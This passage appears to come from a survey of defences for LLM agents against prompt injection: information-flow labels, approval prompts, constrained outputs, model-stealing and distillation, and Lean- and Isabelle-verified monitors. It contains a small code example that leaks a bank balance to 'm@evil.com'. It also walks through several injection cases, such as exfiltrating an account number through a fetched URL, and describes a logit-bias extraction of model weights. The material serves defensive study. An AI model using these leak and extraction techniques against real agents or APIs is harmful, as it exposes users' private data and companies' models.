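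In Wang and colleagues' system, AuthGraph, a model writes the policy using only the user's request and the tool descriptions, before it sees any outside data. The policy states which tool each important argument must come from. When the agent tries to book the flight, AuthGraph searches the flight search results for the code, doesn't find it and blocks the call. AuthGraph doesn't protect against an attacker who has tampered with the flight search itself. Exact matching also works better for a code that the agent copies than for a paragraph that it writes. Narisetty and colleagues point out that software that sees only a tool's inputs and outputs can't trace how the model turned one into the other.

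### Leaks from a branch not taken

Labels on data can miss information that a program reveals when a secret determines which instructions run. Denning calls this an implicit flow, and calls a direct copy an explicit flow. For example, the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0" never copies a into b, but b may still reveal something about a. If b started at 1 and is still 1 at the end, a was not zero.

Garby and colleagues found a leak of this kind in CaMeL. Their example is an agent that manages a bank account and an attacker who wants to know whether the balance exceeds a certain amount. If the program tests the balance and sends an email inside that branch, CaMeL blocks the email, because it treats everything in the branch as dependent on the secret. But the program can take a detour through two variables. In outline:

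```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL changes a variable's label only when the program assigns it a value, with these results:

| Test | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| `balance > threshold` | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Branch skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
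| `tmp` | Branch skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
| `rich` | The email goes out | No email |

In both cases, `rich` is labeled public but reveals whether the balance exceeds the threshold. A monitor that tracks only the instructions that run can't detect this leak, because it comes from the assignment that the program skipped. Denning's paper includes essentially the same program, credited to J. S. Fenton.

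Denning's remedy was to analyse the program before running it. The compiler finds every variable that a branch could change and adds an instruction that raises the variable's label whether or not the branch runs. This is possible for CaMeL because the whole program exists in advance, but it is much harder for an agent whose model decides each step after the last one.

FIDES deliberately doesn't track implicit flows. According to Costa and colleagues, ruling them out completely (noninterference) would in practice mean banning any call with publicly visible effects once the agent had used a tool that can read secrets. They accept that someone who can see the sequence of tool calls may learn a little from it. Earlier systems for phones and browsers allowed similar leaks.

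How much this matters depends on who writes the program. Injected text can't add lines to a CaMeL program, so an attacker would need the privileged model to accidentally write a program that leaks data, or a user to paste in instructions for one. Still, a guarantee about data flow is weaker than it sounds if it depends on the program being written safely.

A single run of this program reveals one bit, the answer to a yes-or-no question. Many security systems tolerate a leak that small. But an attacker who can get the program to run repeatedly, with a different question each time, can combine the answers, and n bits can distinguish 2<sup>n</sup> possibilities. Twenty well-chosen questions are enough to identify any whole-dollar balance below about a million.

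Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL allows such repetition. Its interpreter tracks labels, but the ordinary loop around it, which tries again after a failure, does not. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. Denning described a similar trick in 1976, in which a program deliberately breaks the rules so that its owner can read the secret from the record of blocked operations. One solution was to record violations only after they exceeded some limit, but this made legitimate programs harder to debug.

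### Who assigns the first labels

The lattice determines the label of everything the agent computes, but someone has to label the data that comes in. Some labels are easy to infer. Costa and colleagues treated an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers, although they note that someone may have shared the email more widely. Mail servers can often authenticate a sender's address. Kolluri and colleagues marked users' posts on simulated GitLab and Reddit sites as untrusted and the sites' own buttons and menus as trusted.

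Other cases are less clear. A company's shared drive may hold a supplier's brochure next to its own payment instructions, and a trusted colleague may forward a message from a stranger. Costa and colleagues say a system could mark a document as trusted after it passes a prompt injection filter, but they warn that relying on such filters can weaken the guarantee. Any malicious instructions the filter missed would then have the full authority of trusted text.

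Developers can also forget to label data. Narisetty and colleagues report that the deployed form of FIDES treats unlabelled data as trusted. Google's template system for web pages did the opposite, encoding every string unless a reviewed function had marked it as safe. Treating unlabelled data as untrusted would be safer for agents too, but it would block more legitimate work until someone had labelled every source.

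FIDES labels a user's whole message as trusted and public by default, including any text the user pasted in. If that text contains an injection and the planning model obeys it, the resulting tool call still passes the trusted-action policy. FIDES would also treat a pasted confidential contract as something anyone may read, which could expose its contents.

FIDES can give a user's message other labels, and an application could mark pasted passages as untrusted. But people often paste text, such as a list of errands from a spouse, because they want the agent to act on it. If that text were marked untrusted, the agent would have to refuse or ask the user under the trusted-action policy.

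### Approval fatigue

When a policy blocks a legitimate action, the system usually asks the user to approve it. Labels can make these requests much rarer. Kolluri and colleagues counted how many approvals an agent using OpenAI's o3-mini would need for the AgentDojo tasks it completed. An agent that asked before every consequential call needed 48.2 approvals on average over five runs of the benchmark. Adding labels and asking only when a check failed cut this to 32.4, and FIDES needed 18.8.

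Prudentia gives the planning model the labels and policies so that it can avoid steps that would need approval. It can also prompt the user to endorse a piece of data instead of approving each action. If an email contains ten errands, the user can endorse the email once, and the agent can then do all ten. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but it completed slightly fewer tasks.

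Endorsing an email also makes each decision riskier, because if the email hides an eleventh errand that the user didn't notice, the attacker's instruction becomes trusted too. The count of approvals also depends on people approving legitimate actions and stopping malicious ones, which Kolluri and colleagues did not test with real users. Like Willison, they warn that frequent requests make people careless.

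Experience with coding agents supports the warning. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports about agents and files, and finds that weaknesses in user review contributed to 105. In 80 of those, the agent's actions were approved automatically, a setting some users turn on to avoid answering hundreds of requests in a session. In 31, the approval request gave the user too little information. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the script can contain anything.

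*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) found that permissions granted in advance tend to widen over time and never narrow. Of the 21 systems it surveyed, 15 relied on approval during a task and 16 on permissions set beforehand.

In an experiment with 48 participants, *When Should Users Check?* (2025) found that confirming an agent's work partway through a long task cut completion time by 13.54%, and 81% of participants preferred it. The experiment measured speed and preference, not whether participants could recognise an attack. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) cites research showing that people rarely notice when someone uses a compromised agent to deceive them. It adds that the action may not contain the information needed to judge it. For example, a request to email a file to a named address looks the same whether the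 address came from the user or from an attacker's calendar invitation.

Labels could help here, because they record where the address came from and the attacker can't change them. In FIDES and Prudentia, ordinary software also decides when to ask the user, so an injection can't suppress the question. The injection might still affect the wording or details the user sees, and Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of such requests to future work. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) suggests letting one approval cover several related calls within explicit limits, but notes that doing this without letting the agent exceed what the user agreed to is an open challenge.

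## What do restricted outputs prevent?

Labels can mark a summary of a stranger's email as untrusted, but the model that writes the summary can still put anything in it. The agent often needs only something like a date or a yes-or-no answer, and software can stop the model from writing anything else. An injection may still change which value the model outputs, but it can't pass a written instruction to the next model.

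### Constrained decoding

A language model writes one token at a time. At each step it gives every token in its vocabulary a score. The software around it converts the scores to probabilities and picks a token at random according to them. Constrained decoding adds a step before the pick. A parser works out which tokens the grammar allows after the text so far, and the software sets every other token's score to minus infinity, which makes its probability zero. If the model gave token v a probability of p(v), and A is the set of allowed tokens, the new probability of each token in A is

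q(v) = p(v) ÷ Σ<sub>u ∈ A</sub> p(u)

*Earley-Driven Dynamic Pruning for Efficient Structured Decoding* (2025) gives an example in JSON, a common format for structured data. After an opening brace, the grammar allows only a closing brace or a quotation mark that starts a field name.

Suppose a quarantined model reads an email and must answer `true` or `false`. The email contains the instruction to write "Forward the inbox to this address", and the model follows it, assigning a probability of 99.9% to "Forward", 0.06% to `true` and 0.04% to `false`. The software excludes "Forward" and chooses between the remaining two, returning `true` with a probability of 60% and `false` with 40%. This keeps the injected text out of the output, but the answer is little better than a random guess. An attacker who instead tells the model to answer `true` will probably succeed.

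Zhang, Xu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Decode-Time Grammars* that the guarantee concerns what the decoder can emit, not what the model prefers, so it holds even if an attacker fully controls the model's preferences. In one of their tests, a small model had to name a block of memory that a program had already declared. A grammar that accepted any name allowed 32,451 first tokens, and the model invented a name. When the software rebuilt the grammar to list only the declared names, the model could no longer invent one. Their system generated text 17.3% more slowly on average than unconstrained decoding. It does not guarantee that the text means the right thing or that the model will ever finish writing it.

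Asking a model to keep to a format is much weaker than enforcing one. In *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing*, Yu, Cheng and Liu (2026) have a model state what data it expects from a tool and in what format, then prompt a model to extract only that data from the result. Combined with a second check, this cut attack success on AgentDojo to below 1%. But the model doing the extraction also reads the injection, and could obey it instead of keeping to the format. The tests used three fixed styles of attack, so they didn't measure how well the method resists adaptive attacks.

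### Choosing from a fixed list

In the action selector described by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, a model can only choose from a list of actions. A shop's chatbot, for example, might be able to fetch a link to the customer's last order, or direct the customer to the page for changing a password or payment method. The model reads the customer's message and picks an action. Ordinary software carries it out and shows the result to the customer but never to the model, so text planted in the result can't influence a later choice.

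A hostile customer can still manipulate the model's choice, but gains nothing if the list contains only actions the customer is already allowed to take. The software has to ensure this, for instance by checking that the order belongs to the person asking. The design also removes much of what makes a language model useful. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that a file assistant restricted to ready-made commands mostly loses the ability to search for files by topic.

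Map-reduce keeps some of that ability. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounting department. In the "map" step, the software gives each file to a separate model that has no tools and can only answer whether the file is an invoice. In the "reduce" step, another model writes and sends an email with the files that got a yes. An attacker can get a malicious file sent to accounting, but could also do that by forging an invoice. The file can't affect the answer for any other file, as it could if one model read them all together.

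The protection disappears if the second model reads the invoices to describe them in the email. The software should attach the files without showing them to that model. It should also refer to them by number, because an attacker may have chosen the filenames.

Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025), in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, extend this idea to whole agents. Their quarantined model may send the privileged model only whole numbers, decimals, yes-or-no values and choices from a list that the designer has vetted. They built three agents this way and compared them with ordinary versions:

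| Agent | What the quarantined model passes on | Tasks completed, ordinary → restricted | Attack success, ordinary → restricted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | Two scores from 0 to 10 for each product review | 21.8% → 22.4% | 31.7% → 0% |
| Meeting scheduling | Time slots from a fixed list | 90.0% → 91.0% | 63.0% → 0% |
| Bug fixing | Type of bug, file numbers and line numbers | 68.3% → 45.0% | 98.9% → 0% |

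The shopping agent takes the median of the review scores. One fake review among many barely changes the median, but an attacker who writes more than half of the reviews can set it.

Restricting outputs reduced the number of completed bug-fixing tasks by a third, because bug reports explain in prose what should happen and what happens instead. To recover some of those tasks, Jacob and colleagues had a planner write three possible plans without ever seeing the report. A judge that had seen the report then returned only the number of the best plan. An attacker can influence which plan is chosen but can't add any text to it.

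### Counting bits

An output with N permitted values can carry at most log<sub>2</sub>(N) bits. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) derives this limit from information theory and notes that a designer can find it by counting the permitted values, without knowing how the model behaves.

| Permitted output | Number of values | Most it can carry |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 bit |
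| One of eight categories | 8 | 3 bits |
| A score from 0 to 10 | 11 | About 3.5 bits |
| A ten-digit number | 10 billion | About 33.2 bits |
| Thirty lower-case letters or underscores | About 10<sup>43</sup> | About 143 bits |

FIDES can add an output's type to its security label, and it orders types by how much information they can carry. A policy can then let an untrusted yes-or-no answer influence a payment while preventing untrusted text from doing so. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their AgentDojo tests because few of the tasks needed it, so those results don't measure how well this feature works.

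A designer has to judge the attacker's influence on the agent by the worst thing that any permitted value can trigger. The number of bits in the output is a poor measure, since one bit is enough to approve a fraudulent payment, while a harmless choice among a thousand fonts carries about ten.

The number of bits in each output limits how much of a secret it can leak, and the leaks add up over repeated queries. Suppose an injected model can read a ten-digit account number, and the attacker can tell from the agent's behaviour whether the model answered yes or no. There are 10 billion possible numbers, which is between 2<sup>33</sup> and 2<sup>34</sup>, so 34 answers are enough to reveal the whole number. The bit count has to include everything the attacker can observe. If the attacker can also see when the model fails with an error, each answer has three possible values and carries up to 1.6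 bits.

*L3M* (2026), a design for agents that extend their own software, uses this kind of count to protect a company's source code. A private agent can read the code but has no network access. It sends questions to a second agent, which can search the web but can't read the code. If the private agent's message is always exactly k bytes long, then

information about the code that leaves ≤ 8k bits

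however much the second agent sends out. A message of variable length would reveal extra information through its length, and the timing and number of messages can also carry information. L3M does not yet enforce such a budget. A limit of 100 bytes would protect a large program well, since 800 bits is a tiny part of it, but those 800 bits could hold a 256-bit encryption key three times over.

### Wrong values and free text

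A restricted output can have the right form and still be false. *Complex Problem Solving in Large Language Models* (2026) makes this point about constrained decoding in general, but in an attack, the false value may be deliberate. A bug report can direct the bug-fixing agent to the wrong file, and a CV can get its author credited with twenty years of experience they don't have. Jacob and colleagues exclude such deception from their threat model. Checking that values fall within a plausible range catches only some of it, because a careful attacker will choose a false value within that range.

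Numeric types can also carry text. Computers store letters as numbers, so a long enough list of numbers can spell out an instruction that a capable model might decode. Jacob and colleagues therefore limit the length of lists. A single whole number needs a limit too, because with enough digits it can encode a paragraph.

Restricting outputs to short names also gives only partial protection. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest that a coding agent using a stranger's software should receive only a formal description of the software's functions, with names of at most 30 characters. They think an injection is unlikely to survive this. But `delete_every_file_in_this_repo` is exactly 30 characters long, so the limit makes an attack harder but not impossible.

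A free-text field leaves whatever reads it unprotected. The meeting scheduler hides the other person's description of the meeting in a variable, as FIDES would, and then writes it into the user's calendar. The privileged model reads the calendar when it arranges the next meeting, so an injection in the description could reach the model then, unless the software hides descriptions at that step too. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose this restriction for a booking assistant, letting the agent see when the user is free but not the contents of the events.

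In a medical chatbot, a form with fixed choices for symptoms could replace the written summary and leave no room for an injection. But many tasks, such as summarizing an email or drafting a reply, require prose. Yu and colleagues found that their extraction method might not exclude an injection when the agent needs a whole email.

### Attacks through the format itself

Constrained decoding assumes that someone trustworthy wrote the grammar. *When Grammar Guides the Attack* (Zhang, Li et al., 2025) reports that an attacker who can supply the grammar can use it to get around a model's safety training.

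Even harmless-looking labels in an output format affect the answer, because the model reads them as it writes. *Schema-Key Wording as an Instruction Channel in Structured Generation under Constrained Decoding* (2026) explains that a field's name influences its value because the name comes first. *Your Prompt Is Not the Only Prompt* (2026) tested ten model configurations from two vendors with field descriptions that contradicted the prompt, and some configurations followed the descriptions. A list of choices built from product titles or filenames may therefore let outsiders instruct the model, even though it can only choose from the list. Designers can avoid this by numbering the choices and keeping outsiders' text out of the format.

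A badly chosen grammar can also break an agent even when no one is attacking it. *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) points out that if a grammar permits only the final answer's format, the model can't write a tool call, because the grammar forbids the markers that begin one.

### Links, images and network connections

When an agent has to write prose, its designer can still limit where the prose goes. As with the mail assistant, private data can leak if the screen loads images from addresses the model has written. A link is slightly safer than an image because the user has to click it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe both routes for a shop's chatbot. An attacker tricks a customer into pasting in a malicious prompt, and the chatbot's reply leaks the customer's data through a web address.

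The software can close these routes by refusing to load images and showing links as plain text. If users need links, the software can build them itself, as the action selector does when it fetches a customer's order. Checking only that a link leads to an approved site is weaker, because the rest of the address can still contain data. If the approved site lets anyone upload files or see who visited a page, an attacker may be able to collect the data there.

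Ordinary-looking text can hide data too. An assistant compromised by prompt injection could encode private information in invisible characters and include them in an email the user has approved. These characters are easy to remove, but a model can also encode information in its choice of words. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) describes a monitor that checks an agent's outgoing text and media for known secrets. It also tracks how much hidden information could still get out, so that it can bound leaks through encodings nobody has thought of.

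An agent that runs code also needs limits on the code's network access. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend running the code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that permits only the connections the task needs. If the attacker controls none of the permitted destinations, the code can't send data to the attacker while it runs there. But any result that leaves the sandbox can still carry data. A hijacked coding agent might write the forbidden web request into the program it produces, so that the request goes out when the user runs the program outside the sandbox.

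### Copying a model through its answers

Restricting outputs can also protect the model itself. Companies sell access to their models through an API, an interface that lets a customer's program send prompts and receive answers. *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model* (Carlini, Paleka et al., 2024) showed that some APIs returned enough detail for a customer to recover part of the model's weights.

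The last layer of a language model multiplies an internal list of h numbers by a matrix W to produce a score for every token in the vocabulary:

scores = W · g(p)

Here g(p) is the internal list for prompt p. The vocabulary may contain 100,000 tokens, but the scores can vary in only h independent ways, and h is a few thousand. An attacker who collects the scores for more than h prompts can find h by counting how many of the score lists are independent. The same scores reveal W, apart from an unknown h-by-h matrix that mixes its columns.

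No commercial API returned all the scores. But OpenAI's gave the log-probabilities of the five likeliest tokens, and let customers add a bias to the scores of tokens they chose. The attackers added a large bias B to four tokens at a time, enough to lift them into the top five alongside the model's usual favourite, R. If z is a token's original score and y is the log-probability the API returned, then

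z<sub>i</sub> − z<sub>R</sub> = y<sub>i</sub> − y<sub>R</sub> − B

The researchers recovered every score relative to R by working through the vocabulary four tokens at a time. For less than $20, they extracted the whole final layer of two small OpenAI models and learned that h was 1,024 for ada and 2,048 for babbage. They also found h for GPT-3.5 Turbo but kept the value private at OpenAI's request. They saw no obvious way to extract the earlier layers.

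OpenAI and Google changed their APIs in response, using measures like those the researchers had suggested. These included removing the bias feature, replacing it with a list of banned tokens, and refusing requests that ask for both a bias and log-probabilities. Even if an API refuses that combination, Carlini and colleagues could recover scores without any log-probabilities, though this took about 3.7 queries per score instead of 0.25. Removing the bias feature would stop all their attacks, since each one needs it, but the researchers warn that other settings might leak the same information. Removing the feature would also affect customers who used it to constrain the model's output.

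Detailed outputs also make other attacks easier. *Bits Leaked per Query* (2025) calculates that an attacker needs at least log(1/ε)/I queries to reach an error rate of ε, where I is the information each response reveals about the target. In its experiments, showing the model's reasoning or token scores revealed about half a bit more per query and cut the number of queries a jailbreak typically needed from thousands to tens.

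An imitator can train a model on a stronger model's answers, a method called distillation, without access to the stronger model's weights or scores. Companies routinely distill their own models, but the method also works on a competitor's answers. Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) reports that three Chinese companies made over 16 million exchanges with Claude through about 24,000 fraudulent accounts. In September, the NSA, CISA and FBI accused six companies of similar campaigns in *China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns Against U.S. AI Companies* (2026). Answers that are useful to customers are also useful as training examples, so a company can't rule out imitation by restricting outputs unless it stops selling useful answers.

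Restricting outputs can make imitation less effective by withholding the model's reasoning. OpenAI's API shows customers only a summary of it. In *大规模封号来了！OpenAI开打反蒸馏战* (2026), the Chinese news site 凤凰网 describes an OpenAI experiment in which models trained on the full reasoning mostly scored higher on cybersecurity tests than models trained on summaries and answers. But attackers can sometimes manipulate a model into reproducing its reasoning. OpenAI's *Disrupting a coordinated model-distillation campaign* describes a campaign that did this without breaking the company's encryption or compromising a database.

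The defences against this are largely patches. The Japanese news site 日本時事新聞 reports in *OpenAI、AIの「推論」抜き取り対策を公表 攻撃の成功率は社内試験で54％から0.2％に* (2026) that such attacks succeeded 54.0% of the time against GPT-6 Astra and 0.2% of the time against GPT-6.2 Astra in OpenAI's internal tests. Anthropic's *Strengthening our defenses against distillation attacks* (2026) gives early evidence that new methods have cut the data imitators collect by around 90% to 99%. At the scale of the campaigns Anthropic described in February, a 99% cut would still leave about 160,000 exchanges.

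## Which components can be verified, and what do the proofs cover?

Planners, labels and output limits move security decisions out of the model and into ordinary code, which has bugs. A proof can rule out many of them, as it did for the seL4 kernel. For agents, researchers have tried to prove properties of the software around the model, the policy that this software enforces, and the neural network itself. They have made the most progress with the software, because those proofs need to assume little or nothing about how the model behaves.

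### A programming language with a proof

After finding leaks in CaMeL, Garby and colleagues built LLMbda, a small language for writing agents. Every value in an LLMbda program has a label, such as "secret" or "untrusted", and so does the conversation with the model. When the program sends the model a message, the conversation takes on the message's label, and the model's reply inherits it. If the reply is a program, everything it computes inherits the label too.

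The commands `fork` and `clear`, which copy and empty a conversation, let the model read an email without affecting the main conversation.

LLMbda also prevents leaks from branches that a program doesn't take. Suppose a program sends the model "Set x = true" only if a secret is true, and later prompts the model for x. If the secret is false, the program sends nothing, so the conversation would stay public and the answer would reveal the secret. LLMbda therefore stops any program that tries to write to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on a secret.

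The main theorem about the language establishes termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. If two runs of a program differ only in their secret inputs, an observer who sees only public results can't tell them apart. Likewise, changing only the untrusted inputs doesn't affect results labelled as trusted. Because a language model samples its words at random, the theorem compares the probabilities of results. It doesn't rule out a secret affecting whether the program finishes, and a program that the interpreter stops for breaking a rule counts as unfinished.

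More precisely, take two sets of inputs that look the same to the observer. Let μ(q) be the probability that the program finishes with visible result q on one set, and ν(q) the probability on the other. Each may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the chance that the program never finishes. The theorem states that there is a function ω such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, with Σ ω(q) ≤ 1

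For example, suppose a program prints "yes" or "no" with equal probability when a secret bit is 0, and when the bit is 1, it prints "yes" half the time and otherwise hangs. The theorem allows this, because the probabilities for 0 can serve as ω. It rules out a program that always prints "yes" for 0 and "no" for 1, because ω would have to give both answers a probability of 1.

The statistical distance between the two sets of results is therefore at most the average chance of not finishing, so a program that always finishes reveals nothing. In the example, the distance and the average chance are both 25%.

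Garby and colleagues proved the theorem in Lean, a programming language that is also a proof assistant. The theorem covers every LLMbda program, including those a model writes during a run. The researchers also wrote the interpreter in Lean and proved that its results have the probabilities the theory predicts, assuming that the model's replies follow fixed probabilities for each conversation. The theorems therefore apply to the program that calls the model, except for the code that handles the network connection.

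Some tasks require an agent to act on untrusted data, so LLMbda lets a program "endorse" a value, which relabels it as trusted. Endorsement weakens the protection against injected data, but another theorem shows that it can't weaken the protection of secrets.

### LLMbda on AgentDojo's banking tasks

Garby and colleagues tested an LLMbda agent called Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. The model writes a program and tries it on an artificial account until it works. The agent then runs it on the user's data. Errors caused by untrusted data never reach the planner, so Randori avoids the leak that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's retry loop.

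Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs, which covered three models, nine attacks per task and three repetitions. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The planner had endorsed the contents, because otherwise the agent couldn't have done the task.

In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed a tool that the agent's plan would never use, so planning before reading was generally enough to stop it. The other 47 combinations accounted for 423 runs and both successful attacks. Because the runs repeat the same cases, even if one model resisted every attack in these 47, we could conclude only that it resists at least 92.4% of such attacks, at 95% confidence.

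When nobody was attacking, Randori completed 75% of tasks with GPT-5.2. CaMeL completed 66.7% with its policies off and 37.5% with them on. With so few tasks, the margins of error are around 20 points or more, so the difference between Randori and CaMeL with policies off is too small to tell them apart. Randori also enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, which makes the comparison with policies on less fair. With another model, Qwen3.7-plus, Randori's score fell from 75% to 62.5% when endorsement was removed.

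The theorems depend on developers labelling each source correctly and putting a check on every sensitive tool. They also describe a closed world in which all data sources are part of the program. Garby and colleagues have yet to extend them to outside tools.

### Comparison with an agent that never obeys

Noninterference is too strict for many useful agents. A calendar assistant that answers meeting requests reveals the user's availability to anyone who asks, including attackers, so it violates noninterference even when it works as intended.

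*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* instead compares the agent with an imaginary reference agent. Both follow the same plan, and the same monitor allows or refuses their tool calls, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. The agent is relatively secure if, for any two possible values s₁ and s₂ of the user's private data,

the attacker can tell s₁ from s₂ using the real agent ⇒ the attacker can tell s₁ from s₂ using the reference agent

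An injection that makes the assistant send the user's calendar passes this test, because a genuine meeting request would have revealed the same information. One that makes it include a password reset code fails, because no meeting request would reveal the code. The idea comes from research on processors that run instructions early, based on predictions, and can leak data when a prediction is wrong. That research uses a processor that runs every instruction in order as the reference.

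Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise an email. The agent plans to look up the user's account number, read the email and show a summary. It also has a tool for fetching web pages, which the plan never uses. The attacker's email tells the agent to fetch a page whose address contains the account number. If the model obeys, the number reaches the attacker's server. The reference agent fetches nothing, so this summariser is insecure.

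A fence fixes the problem by having the monitor withdraw the fetching tool as soon as the agent reads the email. The model can still request the page, but the monitor silently blocks the request, so the attacker sees exactly what the reference agent would have shown.

The timing of the fence matters. Suppose the agent can send messages, and its plan includes a step that locks the sending tool:

| Order of steps | What an injected message can leak |
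|---|---|
| Read the email, read a secret, lock | The secret |
| Read the email, lock, read a secret | Private data already in memory, such as from an earlier session |
| Lock, read the email, read a secret | Nothing |

An agent that has to reply to the email can't lock the sending tool first, but the user could approve each reply. If the approval covers the tool, it allows the next message regardless of its content. An injected call can then use the approval to send private data, and the monitor will refuse the reply the user meant to approve because the approval has already been used.

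If the approval covers the exact message, an injected call gets through only when it is identical to the approved reply. An attacker who can see when messages are sent can still learn a little. If the private data matches the approved reply, the injected call sends the reply one step early, so the timing reveals the match.

### The fence theorem

The fence theorem shows that a fence makes every plan relatively secure under these conditions:

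- The monitor withdraws every tool that an injection can call, no later than the first time the agent reads untrusted content.
- No trusted input gives any of those tools back.
- Each injection produces a single tool call.
- The model obeys injections on a schedule fixed in advance. It may put any private data into the call, but it can't decide when to act by looking at a secret or at the monitor's answers.
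- The attacker sees the content and order of the messages that get through, but not their timing or the refused requests.

The proof matches the two agents step by step. When the real agent makes an injected call, the monitor refuses it and the reference agent waits. All other steps are the same for both.

The basic theorem covers runs that end. An agent that handles one email after another needs its tools back for each email, and the software can restore them safely only in a fresh session, after clearing the old email from the model's context. The proof for endless runs also assumes that the model doesn't keep following injected instructions forever.

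The theorem doesn't cover actions that do harm without leaking anything, such as deleting a file. It also excludes multi-agent systems, malicious tool descriptions, planner mistakes, and tools whose reply depends on the request, such as a search engine run by the attacker. Agents whose model chooses each call as it goes have no fixed plan, so there is no reference agent to compare them with.

Relative security also allows some injections that leak far more than the agent otherwise would. Suppose an agent tells anyone who guesses a secret number whether the guess is right, and an injection makes it send the number itself. The agent still counts as relatively secure because, for any two possible numbers, the attacker could have told them apart by guessing one of them. A stricter version of the definition, which fixes the reference agent's input before the secret is known, rejects this agent,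 and the fence theorem holds for that version too.

Nor does the definition measure usefulness. A monitor that refuses every call passes, because the reference agent is just as useless.

Brijesh Dongol checked his paper's theory and 25 example agents in about 31,600 lines of Isabelle, another proof assistant. Claude Code helped write the theorems and proofs, and Isabelle verified every step. AI should greatly reduce the effort such proofs require, which was high for seL4. People still have to check that the definitions mean what they should. Dongol did this by comparing each definition in the paper with its Isabelle version.

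### Verified policy engines

A fence is a very simple policy. Companies have more complicated rules, such as letting an agent exchange an order only after the customer confirms. Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026), in *LEANGUARD*, describe a monitor that checks each tool call against rules written in Lean. It uses this formula:

allow ⇔ at least one permission applies, every requirement holds, no prohibition applies, and no check fails with an error

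A rule can refer to past events, such as requiring the agent to look up an order before changing it. The monitor gets its facts from the company's database and its own record of events. It never treats text in a tool's output as evidence, so an injected note claiming that the customer has already agreed makes no difference.

Sankar and colleagues proved that the code allows a call only if the call satisfies the rules, under a separate logical definition of what the rules mean. The proof covers all policies and histories, so the monitor doesn't need a new proof for each call.

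On τ²-bench, a customer service benchmark, agents made at least 33 calls that the rules forbade when unprotected and none with LeanGuard. When the monitor also told agents which rule they had broken, they completed 70.9% of tasks, compared with 72.7% without protection, a difference that chance could explain. Lean can also search for a small change that would make a refused call acceptable, and prove that the rules allow the changed call. It found one for 88 of 252 refusals caused by a wrong value in the call, though the agents in these tests never received the suggestions.

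On DTap, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks, LeanGuard cut the success rate of direct attacks from 57.9% to 5.9%, and of indirect ones from 22.3% to 3.8%. The policy let agents read data but not change it, so they completed only 12.5% of legitimate tasks, down from 53.1%. On telecom tasks, which rarely require changes, the agents did as well as before, and the success rate of direct attacks fell from 55.1% to 2.4%.

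Some attacks succeeded without a forbidden call because the harm was in the agent's reply. In customer service and travel, these attacks still succeeded 30.2% of the time with LeanGuard, compared with 41.0% without it.

Rules on tool calls are hard to apply when the tool is a command line, because a single command can run a script that does almost anything. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) addresses this by running each command in a disposable copy of the file system and holding back its network requests. The software records the command's requests to the operating system, translates them into simple actions such as "copy" and "upload", and checks these against a policy in Lean. If the actions comply, it makes the changes permanent and releases the network requests. Otherwise, it discards everything.

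For example, an agent may upload a harmless status report. If it then copies a confidential inventory into the report, the software labels the report as sensitive. When the agent runs the same upload command again, the software blocks it.

Lean guarantees that no later rule can override a mandatory one, and that a refused action doesn't change any labels. Developers can also state a property, such as the agent never reading anything labelled "secret", and have Lean prove that the policy maintains it over any number of steps.

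The translation into simple actions has no such proof. Sistla and colleagues tested it by generating many ways of moving the same data and checking that the software recognised them. If the translation misses one, the verified policy is applied to an incomplete record of what happened.

Tether blocked every attack within its scope on two benchmarks of coding agents, and wrongly blocked 2.3% and 5.0% of legitimate runs. That scope excludes attacks involving systems Tether can't trace, such as databases, though it can detect and block all access to those systems. It also excludes attacks that break no data-flow rule, such as writing subtly wrong code.

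*PerMIT* (2026) gives Lean proofs about the memory an agent keeps between sessions, where the protected model sees only endorsed entries. The proofs hold however the model behaves, but only for a single user and under stated deployment conditions.

### Errors in the policy

None of these proofs can show that a policy is right. Sankar and colleagues used 45 rules to cover three areas of customer service. A language model drafted the rules from the written policies, and people corrected the drafts. If both missed an exception, Lean would enforce the rule without it.

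Mondl, Maisel and Brock automate more of this work in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026). One model translates prompts, tool descriptions and policy documents into formal rules, and another criticises the result. In *VeriGuard* (2025), a model writes both the policy's code and the formal conditions it should meet, and a verifier proves that the code meets them. This catches coding errors, but if the model has misunderstood the request, the code and the conditions may share the misunderstanding, and the proof will still succeed.

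Rules for an agent are also harder to fix in advance than rules for an ordinary app. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to comment on issue 745 on GitLab, a site for software projects. The agent should be able only to open that issue and write in its comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs different permissions. By then it has read text from strangers, which could influence any model that works out the new permissions.

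### Policies that depend on probabilities

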